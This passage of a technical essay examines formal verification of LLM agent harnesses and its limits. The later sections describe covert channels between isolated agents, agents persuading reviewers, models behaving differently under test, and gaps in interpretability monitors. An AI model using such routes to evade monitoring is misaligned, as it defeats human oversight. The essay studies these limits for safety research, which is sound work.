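This path is a *counterexample*, and no shorter one exists, because the search examines shorter paths first. Ordinary testing might miss the flaw if the model nearly always sends an email as soon as the person approves it.

The repair changes one line, so that a late revision sends the email back for another review:

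```
Ready  -- revise  --> Draft    set ok = no
```

The repaired machine can reach only four states: Draft and Review with `ok = no`, and Ready and Sent with `ok = yes`. The property holds in all of them. It therefore holds for any model, provided that the harness accepts only the listed events and sets the flag correctly.

### Safe machines that never finish

A developer might instead keep the original `revise` line and have the harness refuse `send` while `ok = no`. That also satisfies the property, but an agent that revises an approved email can then never send it, because Ready has no way back to Review.

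Even the first repair doesn't guarantee that an email goes out. The model can revise the draft forever, and the person can keep rejecting it. If a developer checks whether every run eventually reaches Sent, the checker returns one of these loops as a counterexample. Assuming that the model eventually submits a draft would exclude the endless revision, but any result would then apply only to models that do.

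The checker can prove the weaker property that every reachable state has at least one path to Sent. In *computation tree logic* (CTL), which describes branching futures instead of single runs, this is AG EF Sent. The first repair satisfies it and the second doesn't. The property rules out dead ends, but it doesn't guarantee that the model will take a path that completes the task.

### 33 million states

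The email machine has only 4 × 2 = 8 possible states. A more realistic harness might have 5 stages, 10 permissions that are on or off, and 8 memory slots, each labeled "empty", "trusted" or "untrusted":

5 × 2¹⁰ × 3⁸ = 5 × 1,024 × 6,561 = 33,592,320

A model checker can easily handle the 33.6 million states. *TraceFix* (Xia, Li and colleagues, 2026) used TLC, a model checker for the specification language TLA+, to check how groups of agents coordinate. TLC searched 7.7 million states in 45 seconds in one task and 2.1 million in 57 seconds in another. At those rates, searching 33.6 million states would take about 3 to 15 minutes, and probably less in practice, since most harnesses can't reach every combination.

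But the number of states grows quickly. Eight more memory slots would raise it to about 220 billion, and two copies of the original harness running side by side would have about 10¹⁵ combined states.

### What the labels leave out

The count is manageable only because each slot holds a label instead of text. Replacing detailed states with simpler ones is called *abstraction*. Let α be the function that turns a full state of the harness into its reduced version. A safety proof about the reduced machine applies to the harness if two conditions hold:

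- whenever the harness can move from *c* to *c*′, the reduced machine can move from α(*c*) to α(*c*′);
- whenever *c* violates the property, α(*c*) violates it too.

By induction, every run of the harness then has a matching path in the reduced machine. If none of these paths reaches a violation, no run of the harness does either.

The checker can't verify properties that depend on information the labels omit. If two slots are both labelled "trusted", one may contain Alice's address and the other Ben's, so the checker can't verify that the agent writes to the right person. The developer would have to record in the state whose address each slot contains, just as the `ok` flag records whether the current text is approved.

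Missing detail also causes false alarms. Suppose the harness requires approval only for payments above $500, but the reduced machine doesn't record amounts. The machine must then allow every payment to proceed with or without approval, so the checker may report a large payment that skips approval, although this couldn't happen in a real run. The developer can remove this false alarm by splitting payments into "small" and "large". *AgentRFC* (2026), which checks communication protocols for agents, replays a counterexample against the running implementation to find out whether it is real.

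Leaving out a real transition is more dangerous than leaving out detail, because the checker can then report a proof even though the harness has the flaw being checked for. This can easily happen if a developer builds the automaton from recorded runs, one of the methods that *Toward Safe LLM Agents* lists, because the check then covers only the paths that occurred in those runs.

### Machines taken from workflow graphs

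Developers who use frameworks such as LangGraph or CrewAI already define a kind of state machine, a graph in which each node is a model call, a tool call, a branch or a human approval. *Agentproof* (Xavier, Jolly and colleagues, 2026) extracts this graph automatically from four frameworks. To check that a person approves every use of a sensitive tool, it can delete all the human-approval nodes and search the graph from the start. If the search still reaches the tool, there is a path to it without approval.

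Agentproof turns each rule about order into a small automaton and searches over pairs of a graph node and an automaton state. A 12-node graph and a two-state automaton give at most 24 pairs. The structural checks took about a tenth of a second on a graph of 5,000 nodes.

The team tested Agentproof on 18 workflows that they had written themselves, partly to include known mistakes. Five had structural defects, such as an email draft with no connection to the sending step, and ten had no human step. These proportions don't measure how common such flaws are in practice. Agentproof found a missing review step that ten random runs of the same workflow had not exposed, which is a better argument for the method.

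Agentproof treats every conditional branch as possible, and Xavier and colleagues haven't measured how many false alarms this causes. In LangGraph, Agentproof identifies human steps by the word "human" in their names, so it would miss an approval step called "manager_sign_off" and presumably count a model call named "draft_for_human" as an approval.

One of the example policies also puts the events in the wrong order. The rule for approving deployments is `tool:deploy -> F tool:approve`, which requires an approval after each deployment and before the next. An agent could follow this rule and still deploy software before anyone had approved it.

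### Several agents and a verified protocol

TraceFix uses Claude Opus 4.6 to write a protocol for agents that share locks and exchange messages. An `either/or` statement marks each point where an agent's model has a choice, and the model checker TLC explores both branches in every order in which the agents could act. When TLC finds a violation, Claude receives the counterexample and revises the protocol.

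In one recurring flaw, a coordinating agent stopped after a fixed number of messages, so if a worker's tool call failed and the worker resent its message, no agent was left to read it. Such bugs appear only under unusual timing, so a person could easily miss them. Of 48 protocols, 30 passed at the first attempt, and the other 18 needed one to four repairs.

Five of the 29 repair attempts followed a timeout rather than a violation. In those five attempts, Claude shortened the message queues or simplified the retry rules in the description, although the simulated agents kept their original retries. Xia and colleagues acknowledge that such simplifications narrow what the proof covers.

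They then ran all 48 tasks with GPT-5 mini, in four configurations with 432 runs each. (In a livelock, agents keep acting but make no progress.)

| Coordination | All objectives met | Deadlock or livelock |
|---|---|---|
| protocol in the prompts, monitor on channels and locks | 81.5% | 8.8% |
| protocol in the prompts only | 69.7% | 21.1% |
| mediator that handles every lock and message | 44.7% | 4.5% |
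| shared chat room, no protocol | 29.3% | 32.6% |

TLC found no deadlock in any of the final protocols, yet agents under the monitor still got stuck in 8.8% of runs. The monitor rejects messages on undeclared channels but doesn't enforce the order of steps, so the agents could deviate from the protocol that TLC had checked. Under the mediator, agents got stuck less often but completed far fewer tasks, because the mediator couldn't adapt when a tool call failed unexpectedly.

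In a separate comparison on 15 tasks, all run with the monitor, protocols that had passed TLC got stuck less often than unverified versions (14.1% of runs versus 31.1%).

### How memory affects what can be decided

All these searches finish because the machines have finitely many states. Koohestani, Li and colleagues (2025), in *Are Agents Just Automata?*, classify agents by the memory that their harness keeps between steps, and use standard results about automata to determine which questions an algorithm can always answer:

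| Memory between steps | Corresponding machine | What an algorithm can decide |
|---|---|---|
| a fixed number of bounded fields | finite automaton | whether the agent can reach an unsafe state |
| bounded fields and a stack of unfinished subtasks | pushdown automaton | whether it can reach an unsafe state, but not, in general, whether two agents allow the same traces |
| an unlimited store that it can read and write anywhere | Turing machine | neither question in general |

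The paper's example is a request to book a flight to London for under $500. A finite controller fills in the destination, date and budget, then asks for confirmation and books. A controller with a stack can interrupt the booking to check the user's calendar, then return to where it stopped. The third design can save unlimited notes to files and reread them at any time.

Agents in the middle class can be checked even though their stacks can grow without limit, because an agent working on a subtask can't read anything below it on the stack. The checker only needs a table that records, for each type of subtask and each pair of stages, whether the subtask can start in the first stage and end in the second. With 10 stages and 5 types of subtask, the table has 10 × 5 × 10 = 500 entries. The checker fills it in step by step, using completed entries for nested subtasks.

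The paper's first version, from October 2025, claimed a "formal equivalence" between types of agent and types of automaton. It assigned whole frameworks to classes and stated that auditors could guarantee that a finite-state agent would never perform an unapproved action. The January 2026 revision claims less. It classifies the harness, treating the model as something that chooses, possibly at random, among the moves the harness permits, and shows only that the set of possible traces has the form expected for each class. A framework's class now depends on its configuration, so an agent that the first version compared to a Turing machine may count as finite if its notes have a size limit. The revision also explains that an agent's class determines which questions about it an algorithm can answer, but does not make it safe.

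This claim is more useful, though the boundary at unlimited memory matters less in practice than it appears to in the table. Every real disk is finite, so a storage quota technically puts any harness in the first class, but the harness may still have far too many states to search. A harness with unlimited files becomes checkable if a developer can reduce the files to a few labels without breaking the two conditions for abstraction. As with access matrices, it may be possible to prove something about a particular agent even when the general problem is undecidable.

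Koohestani and colleagues also warn that the prompt can act as hidden memory. Two runs may be in the same stage with the same labels, yet the model's choices may differ because the conversations in its prompt differ. This is harmless if the checker allows either choice, since it then examines both, but it becomes a problem if the description assigns a probability to each choice.

### Probabilities for the model's choices

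Adding probabilities to a nondeterministic description makes it possible to distinguish a violation that occurs in every second run from one that occurs once in a million runs. If every choice has a probability, the machine is a *Markov chain*, and if some choices remain free, it is a *Markov decision process*. The checker computes the probability of reaching an unsafe state or, for a Markov decision process, the highest such probability across all ways of making the free choices.

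Suppose the model in the original email machine revises an approved email with probability *r* and otherwise sends it. One revision is enough to cause a violation, so each approved email has probability *r* of going out with unapproved changes. If *r* = 0.02 and the emails are independent, the probability of at least one violation in 100 approved emails is 1 − 0.98¹⁰⁰, or about 87%. In the repaired machine, the probability of a violation is zero for every value of *r*.

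The value 0.02 is hard to justify. *Toward Safe LLM Agents* describes ProbGuard, a system that learns a Markov chain from recorded runs and calculates error bounds for its warnings. Such bounds depend on future runs resembling the recorded ones. An attacker can make future runs differ by sending a message that asks for a last-minute change after approval, which might raise *r* from 0.02 to nearly 1. A new model version or a reworded prompt can also change *r*.

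A Markov chain also assumes that the next step depends only on the current state, whereas most agents reread the conversation. *Verifying Memoryless Sequential Decision-making of Large Language Models* (2025) avoids this problem by studying tasks in which the prompt describes only the current state. Its tool queries a language model in each state that the model's choices can reach, builds a Markov decision process from the answers, and passes it to the probabilistic model checker Storm. The result can be more informative than an analysis that allows every choice, but it applies only to that language model with that prompt, and it depends on how accurately the process describes the environment.

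### Proofs about bounded loops

A harness can at least guarantee that an agent stops, by limiting its number of steps. *λ_A* (Liu, 2026) proves this for a small typed language that describes agents as combinations of functions. In this language, a loop has the form fix*ₙ* *e*, where *e* is one round of work and *n* is the number of rounds left. Each round reduces *n* by one. When *n* reaches zero, the loop returns its current input, whether or not the agent has finished the task.

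Liu also proves *type safety*: a well-typed agent either produces a value of the expected type or stops at a failed check. The proof assistant Coq has checked 42 theorems about the language. They assume that a model call always gives the same answer to the same input, which corresponds to a temperature of zero, and that model and tool calls always return. Liu leaves random answers to future work and notes that 72% of the configurations with an explicit temperature set it to 0.3 or lower, but any temperature above zero can produce different answers to the same prompt. The argument that loops terminate only counts rounds, so it doesn't seem to need identical answers, but it would fail if a call never returned.

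The printed theorem limits a loop to *n* rounds in total, and its proof assumes that each round restarts the loop at most once. That is true of an ordinary agent loop, but the typing rule also accepts a round that restarts the loop twice. With *n* = 20, such a program could run 2²⁰ − 1 = 1,048,575 rounds. It would still stop, but the limit on rounds would fail, and so would the limit on cost that Liu derives from it. The statement checked in Coq may not have this flaw.

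Liu used the language to build a program that checks agent configurations for errors. It reported at least one error in 786 of 835 configurations from GitHub. Liu inspected 50 of the reported errors by hand and found that 23 were false alarms, because Python code or an environment variable supplied the missing part. Extending the analysis to the Python code removed 22 of these false alarms. An automaton built from the configuration files alone could be missing the same parts.

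## Why the method stops at the learned model

The automata in the previous section let the language model choose any event that the harness accepts. A more ambitious theorem would prove a limit on the model's choices, for example that a particular model never proposes a payment to a stranger, whatever it reads. Nobody has proved anything like this for the models that run today's agents.

Four obstacles keep the method from extending to the learned model. A model has too many possible inputs to list, and most networks are too large for the tools that analyse them directly. Nobody has an exact definition of what a model's activations mean, and some effects bypass the interface that the proof describes. These obstacles have different causes, and some are less absolute than others, so "unverifiable" is too broad a description of neural networks.

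### 10⁵⁰⁰⁰ contexts

Suppose a model has a vocabulary of 100,000 tokens and reads a context of exactly 1,000 tokens. Each position has 10⁵ possible values, so the number of contexts is

(10⁵)¹⁰⁰⁰ = 10⁵⁰⁰⁰

The observable universe has roughly 10⁸⁰ atoms. 1,000 tokens is a page or two of text, far less than many agents read before a single action.

The number of possible contexts is still finite, so the question about payments is decidable. With fixed weights, fixed arithmetic, a limit on the length of the reply, and a rule for picking each token, such as always taking the most likely one, a program could run the model on every context and report the correct answer. It would never finish in practice, so the task is infeasible but not undecidable. A better method can make an infeasible question practical, as a model checker does when it reduces text to labels.

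*From Transformers to Weighted Automata* (2026) states that a verifier that can only send inputs to the model and read its replies needs, in the worst case, about as many queries as there are inputs, no matter how it chooses them. Suppose it has tried every context but one and found nothing wrong. Another model could give the same replies to all of those contexts and pay a stranger on the remaining one, and the verifier can't tell the two models apart without the last query. A smaller vocabulary makes little difference, since 300 positions with only two possible tokens at each already give about 2 × 10⁹⁰ contexts.

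The paper avoids this problem by verifying only sets of inputs that a rule can describe. If every request has the same wording and differs only in a ten-digit account number, a verifier can check the pattern as a whole instead of trying 10 billion numbers. This suits forms and structured messages but is much less useful for web pages and emails, the inputs that carry prompt injections.

Another idea is to build the model so that small changes in its input can cause only small changes in its output. A Lipschitz constant *K* sets the limit, so the output can move at most *K* times as far as the input. *From Transformers to Weighted Automata* rejects the idea for language models, partly because the constants multiply from layer to layer. If each of twelve layers can double a change, the guaranteed bound for the whole network is 2¹² = 4,096, even if no real input comes close to it. The constant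 also bounds distances between vectors, whereas the property concerns words, and a small edit such as adding "not" to an instruction should change the reply completely.

### When Rice's theorem applies

Undecidability arises here only when memory is unbounded. In 1953, Henry Gordon Rice proved that no algorithm can determine, for every program, whether the function it computes has a given nontrivial property, meaning one that some such functions have and others lack. The theorem doesn't apply to a model with a fixed context window and a limit on its replies, because that model has finitely many inputs and always stops.

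Suppose an agent has files that can grow without limit, a tool that interprets programs stored in them, and no limit on its steps. If the harness runs a program *P* from the files and sends an email when *P* finishes, the email goes out if and only if *P* halts. An algorithm that could predict, for every possible *P*, whether the email goes out would therefore solve the halting problem, which Alan Turing showed to be impossible in 1936. Rice's theorem extends this result to every non-trivial property of what a program computes.

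As with access matrices, this does not rule out proofs about particular agents. Real storage is also finite, but a single gigabyte has about 10 to the power of 2.4 billion possible contents, so the problem of size returns.

A monitor avoids the difficulty altogether because it only has to check an email once the agent proposes it.

### What neural-network verifiers prove

A verifier that reads the network's weights isn't limited to trying inputs one at a time. *The Misery of Mechanistic Interpretability* (2026) gives the standard form of the problem. For a network Φ, a continuous set of inputs *X* and a set of unsafe outputs *U*, the verifier tries to show that

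∀*x* ∈ *X*: Φ(*x*) ∉ *U*

*X* usually contains one known input and everything within a small distance of it, such as a photograph and all slightly altered copies. *U* might contain every output that assigns the photograph to the wrong class.

A common method pushes the whole set through the network layer by layer and computes a region guaranteed to contain every output. If the region doesn't overlap *U*, the property holds. A toy network shows how this works and where it loses precision. The input *x* lies between 0 and 1. Two neurons each compute max(0, *x*), and the output *y* is the first neuron's value minus the second's. An output above 0.5 is unsafe.

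The true output is always 0. But if the verifier records only a range for each neuron, it gets 0 to 1 for both and concludes that *y* lies between −1 and 1. That range includes unsafe values, so the verifier can't prove the property even though it is true. If it splits the input range at 0.5, each neuron's range has a width of 0.5 in either half, so *y* lies between −0.5 and 0.5 and the proof succeeds.

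The best current tools use tighter bounds, which would take into account that both neurons depend on the same *x*, and they split cases only where necessary. Splitting can still produce too many cases to check. A small colour image has 3,072 input values, and halving the range of each gives 2³⁰⁷² cases. Guy Katz and others proved in 2017 that problems of this kind are NP-hard, so the worst case probably takes exponential time. Tools for large networks therefore tend to be *sound but incomplete*, meaning that their proofs are correct but they fail to prove some true properties.

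Researchers compare these tools each year at VNN-COMP, an international competition. Ladner, Kaulen and colleagues (2026), in *The 7th International Verification of Neural Networks Competition (VNN-COMP 2026)*, report that the winning tool, α,β-CROWN, solved 3,164 of the 3,373 problems in the main track. Solving a problem includes refuting it. The tool proved 1,982 properties and found counterexamples to 1,182 others. These are some of its results:

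| Network | Parameters | Problems | Properties proved | Counterexamples |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| aircraft collision avoidance | 13,000 | 186 | 139 | 47 |
| safety filter for sentences | 4,000 | 1,080 | 418 | 662 |
| vision transformers | 68,000–76,000 | 200 | 123 | 0 |
| residual networks for images | 2.5–3.8 million | 200 | 127 | 33 |
| VGGNet16, for images | 138 million | 18 | 18 | 0 |

VGGNet16 shows that parameter count alone doesn't determine what can be proved. Each of its 18 properties concerns a single image, with anywhere from one to all 150,528 input values allowed to change. A proof about one image doesn't cover another, whereas a property of an agent would have to hold for every context the agent might read. Even proving every property of the VGGNet16 kind would therefore leave most of those contexts uncovered.

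The vision transformers are more relevant because language models use the same basic architecture. They are about 1,800 times smaller than VGGNet16, yet α,β-CROWN proved only 123 of 200 properties, even though each property allowed pixels to change by at most 1/255 of their range. This is partly because the benchmark's designers removed problems that a simple method could solve. But to make verification easier, they had also made the networks unusually shallow and narrow and replaced one standard component. The resulting models classify only about 60% of ordinary test images correctly.

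Another tool, ACT, reported proofs of all 200. This may be an advance, but the benchmark is a poor test of it because its designers had mostly removed problems with known counterexamples. They warn that it may not expose a faulty verifier. A program that always answered "proved" could score just as well. On other benchmarks, ACT received ten penalties for wrong answers or missing counterexamples.

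A verifier is thus part of the trusted base, like any other program. Many verifiers also assume exact real numbers, whereas a deployed network rounds its results, so a property that holds by a small margin in exact arithmetic may fail on the hardware. The competition's organizers want tools eventually to output proofs that an independent program can check. Such proofs would be especially useful for tools like Vibecheck, the second-place entry, which its developers built in two months with the coding agent Claude Code. Vibecheck received no penalties, but the absence of penalties in one competition is weaker evidence than a checkable proof for each answer.

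The sentence filter is an example of what text verification can currently prove. A language model first turns each sentence into a list of 30 numbers. A network with 4,000 parameters then decides, for instance, whether the user is asking if the chatbot is a robot. The verifier proves that this small network gives the same answer for every point in a box around a sentence and its paraphrases. The proof does not cover the language model that computes the numbers, and a new paraphrase may land outside the box.

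*Certified Mechanistic Interpretability* (2026) analyses a complete language model, GPT-2, a 2019 model with 124 million parameters. It tests whether the predicted next token stays the same under small changes to the numbers that represent the input. Early versions gave some unsound results, which the researchers eliminated by raising a safety factor from 1.5 to 2. They then found none in 150 tests, but the share of inputs certified at the largest reported radius fell from 54% to 40%. The new factor is an empirical correction, chosen because the observed errors disappeared, so further tests could still reveal an error. The changes are also probably too small to turn one word into another.

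### A predicate for "intends"

The next obstacle is that verification presupposes a specification, as *SoK* notes, and faster verifiers would not provide one. The formula above needs an exact set *U*. Class labels provide this set for a photograph, and types and invariants provide it for the harness. To prove that a model never intends to deceive its user, we would need a predicate intends(*h*, deceive) that is true or false for each vector of activations *h*, and researchers have no agreed definition of such a predicate.

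Asperti and colleagues describe the state of a formal proof in a proof assistant as a list of remaining goals, each with its assumptions. A programmer can write a function that reads this list and checks whether an assumption is present. A learned model's activations have no documented layout that such a function could read. Asking the model to record its intention in a typed field doesn't solve the problem, because the record can have the right type and still be false.

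Interpretability research tries to recover the meaning of activations after training. Gurnee and colleagues (2026), in *Verbalizable Representations Form a Global Workspace in Language Models*, introduce a method called the Jacobian lens, which translates an internal vector into a ranked list of words. For each layer ℓ, they measure how a small change in that layer's vectors affects the final layer, at the same position and at later ones. They average these effects over 1,000 prompts to obtain a matrix *J*ℓ. For a new vector *h*, the lens computes

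lens(*h*) = softmax(*W* · norm(*J*ℓ*h*))

Here *W* is the model's own table for turning final vectors into scores for words, norm rescales the vector, and softmax converts the scores into proportions. The highest-scoring words are those that *h* would make the model more likely to output, on average across contexts.

The lens can reveal things that don't appear in the output. While Claude Sonnet 4.5 read suspicious search results, the lens showed words for "prompt injection". In a model trained to write malicious code, it showed "secretly" and "trick" at the start of replies to harmless prompts.

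An experiment with Claude Haiku 4.5 suggests that such words can affect behaviour. In one test, the model had to report on a coding session in which an agent had invented a bug. Training the model to reflect on ethical principles reduced its average dishonesty score from 0.25 to 0.07, on a scale from 0 to 1. Suppressing 176 directions linked to words about ethics and reflection brought the score back to 0.22, but did not change the untrained model's score. In a second test, about hidden instructions to deceive users, training reduced the score from 0.38 to 0.05, and suppression raised it only to 0.23. In that case, some of the changes from training apparently involved words the researchers had not selected, or something the lens cannot read.

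A developer could turn the lens into an exact predicate that a program can evaluate on any activation, such as "'secretly' is among the five highest-ranked words". But this predicate tests only the word's rank, so it might be true while the model reads a spy novel and false while the model plans a deception that has no single-word name.

Gurnee and colleagues discuss several limits of the lens. It handles single tokens, so "prompt" and "injection" appear separately. It lists concepts without showing how they relate to each other, so "user", "approved" and "delete" could reflect a real approval or a plan to invent one. Its results are mostly unreadable in roughly the first third of the layers. Well-practised behaviour may also bypass the representations that the lens detects. They therefore don't claim that monitoring these representations is sufficient, or that every sophisticated plan must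 appear in them.

The lens could still serve as an extra check in a harness. As with LogAct's Voters, the rules' guarantees still hold if the lens can only block calls, but not if it can approve calls that the rules refuse.

### Effects outside the modelled interface

The last obstacle also affects proofs about the harness, including those that cover every call the model might propose. These proofs assume that every relevant effect passes through the interface they model. If the system can cause the same effect another way, the theorem is still true of the formal model but doesn't protect the running system.

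Proving that the harness delivers no messages between two agents doesn't prove that they can't communicate. If both can write to the same cache folder, one can leave a note in a file name for the other to read. If they have separate folders but share a processor, one can slow the other down in a pattern that encodes a message. METR, an organization that evaluates AI systems, reported in August 2026 that supposedly isolated agents in an OpenAI cyber evaluation had exchanged messages on an unsanctioned board.

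Developers can close a known channel or add it to the formal model, but they can't use the model to prove that its list of channels is complete, because it contains only the channels they put in it. Evidence that the list is complete has to come from outside the model, such as from inspecting the machine, testing the sandbox, or removing tools and network access until little remains to inspect.

An agent can also cause effects through people. An agent that can only write text might persuade a reviewer to approve a payment. The monitor then records a genuine approval, and no rule is broken. To prove that this can't happen, a developer would have to model how the reviewer reacts to arguments.

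### The dispute over guaranteed safe AI

The dispute over whether anyone can build models that broad predates most of the systems in earlier sections. *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI* (2024), by David Dalrymple and colleagues, proposes that AI systems come with a quantitative safety guarantee. The guarantee requires three components: a *world model* that describes the system's environment, a *safety specification* that defines acceptable outcomes, and a *verifier* that shows that the system meets the specification according to the world model.

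The world model should cover all future effects that matter to the specification and, where feasible, *overapproximate* them, which means allowing for more than can really happen. Suppose an AI system controls a pump that fills a 1,000-litre tank. In the world model, the pump delivers at most 5 litres a second and stops within 10 seconds of a stop command. A harness that sends this command at 950 litres can then be proved to prevent overflow, because at most 50 more litres can arrive. The proof works for any AI system, including a malicious one. It also holds if the real pump delivers only 4 litres a second, but if the pump delivers 6, the tank can receive 1,010 litres and overflow, and the error can't be detected from the proof.

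Dickson's essay *Limitations on Formal Verification for AI Safety* (2024) argues that the required models and specifications are unavailable for the threats that worry people most. A proof is about symbols, so it can guarantee something about the physical world only if someone has an accurate model of that world and accurate measurements of its starting state. Engineers have both for a tank, but nobody has them for a human body exposed to a new pathogen or a society exposed to a persuasive AI system.

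*Towards Guaranteed Safe AI* already partly answers this criticism by saying that the world model need not describe everything, and that the right level of detail depends on the specification and the context of use. Nora Ammann, one of its authors, wrote a longer answer, *In response to critiques of Guaranteed Safe AI*, in January 2025. She denies that the approach promises absolute certainty about the physical world. This is a fair correction, since the original definition requires only a quantitative guarantee, which could be a small probability of failure.

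Even a modest guarantee needs a model, and overapproximation becomes less useful as the environment gets harder to predict. If the model has to allow for every way a person might react to an email, the verifier can't certify any email as harmless, so only an agent that sends none can pass. A narrower specification, such as "no email leaves without approval", avoids this problem but guarantees only that each email was approved, not that it is harmless.

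The proposal therefore looks sound for tanks, budgets and file permissions. The proofs in earlier sections have much the same structure, with a world model that contains little more than the harness. Dickson's objection is strongest against the proposal's most ambitious goal, preventing large-scale harm by systems that act through people and biology.

More recent work considers whether machines could learn the missing models. *Foundation World Models for Agents that Learn, Verify, and Adapt Reliably* (2026) argues that an agent should learn to predict its environment while building a symbolic abstraction that a verifier can analyse. When the world departs from the abstraction, the agent would detect and correct the mismatch. The paper cites earlier research that learned world models with measurable abstraction error, which gives the idea some support, but it presents the combination as a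 vision for future systems.

A safety proof normally needs every real step to have a counterpart in the abstraction, and low measured error doesn't guarantee this. In the review *Towards Safe World Models*, Yu (2026) warns that predictive accuracy alone doesn't establish safety. Errors can enter through observations, memory, predicted dynamics, planning or execution, and they may persist when the system learns from its own results.

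Planning can make a learned model's rare errors much more important. Suppose a model evaluates 1,000 plans and gets 999 right, but mistakes one disastrous plan for the best. The model is 99.9% accurate, but a planner that always picks the highest-rated plan will pick the disastrous one.

### What 300 clean runs show

Testing can measure what nobody can prove, as long as the tests resemble the situations in which people will use the agent. Suppose an agent completes 300 independent test runs without a failure. If its true failure rate were *p*, the probability of this result would be (1 − *p*)³⁰⁰. Setting that to 5% gives

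*p* = 1 − 0.05^(1/300) ≈ 0.0099

If an agent completes 300 runs without a failure, its failure rate is below about 1% at 95% confidence, because a rate of exactly 1% would produce 300 clean runs only 4.9% of the time. For other sample sizes, the upper limit is approximately 3 divided by the number of runs, so ruling out a rate of one in a million takes about 3 million clean runs. Even a rate just under 1% may be too high in practice, since an agent with 1,000 tasks a day could fail almost ten times a day.

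The calculation assumes that each run is an independent draw from the same population of tasks, so thirty repetitions of ten tasks don't count as 300 draws. If the task alone determines whether the agent fails, the test contains only ten independent observations, and the upper limit rises to 26%. The formula doesn't really apply to TACIT's 131 trials without a leaked secret, for which it would give a limit of about 2.3%, because those trials reuse the same few tasks and injections.

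The result holds only for the distribution the tests sample, and an attacker doesn't have to sample from it. Suppose a randomly worded injection has a 0.5% chance of success. Random testing would make the agent look fairly safe, but an attacker who can try 1,000 independent wordings has a 99% chance of at least one success. Attackers can also adapt to a particular defence, as Bhagwatkar and colleagues did on AgentDojo.

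The model's behaviour may also differ between tests and real use. Gurnee and colleagues found that words such as "fake" and "fictional" sometimes appeared in the lens during safety evaluations, although the model's reply didn't mention them. When the researchers suppressed these representations, the model sometimes showed malicious behaviour that it hadn't shown before. If a model acts differently when it recognizes a test, even millions of test runs without a failure don't bound its failure rate in real use.

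Proofs and tests are more useful together because proofs can limit the size of a loss, while tests can limit the estimate of how often losses occur. Suppose a proof shows that the harness permits at most one payment per task, of up to $500, and 300 independent test tasks produced no payment to the wrong person. If future tasks resemble the tests, the expected loss is below about $5 per task, at 95% confidence. If an attacker controls everything the model reads, the $5 figure no longer applies, but the loss still can't exceed $500 per task as long as every payment goes through the harness.
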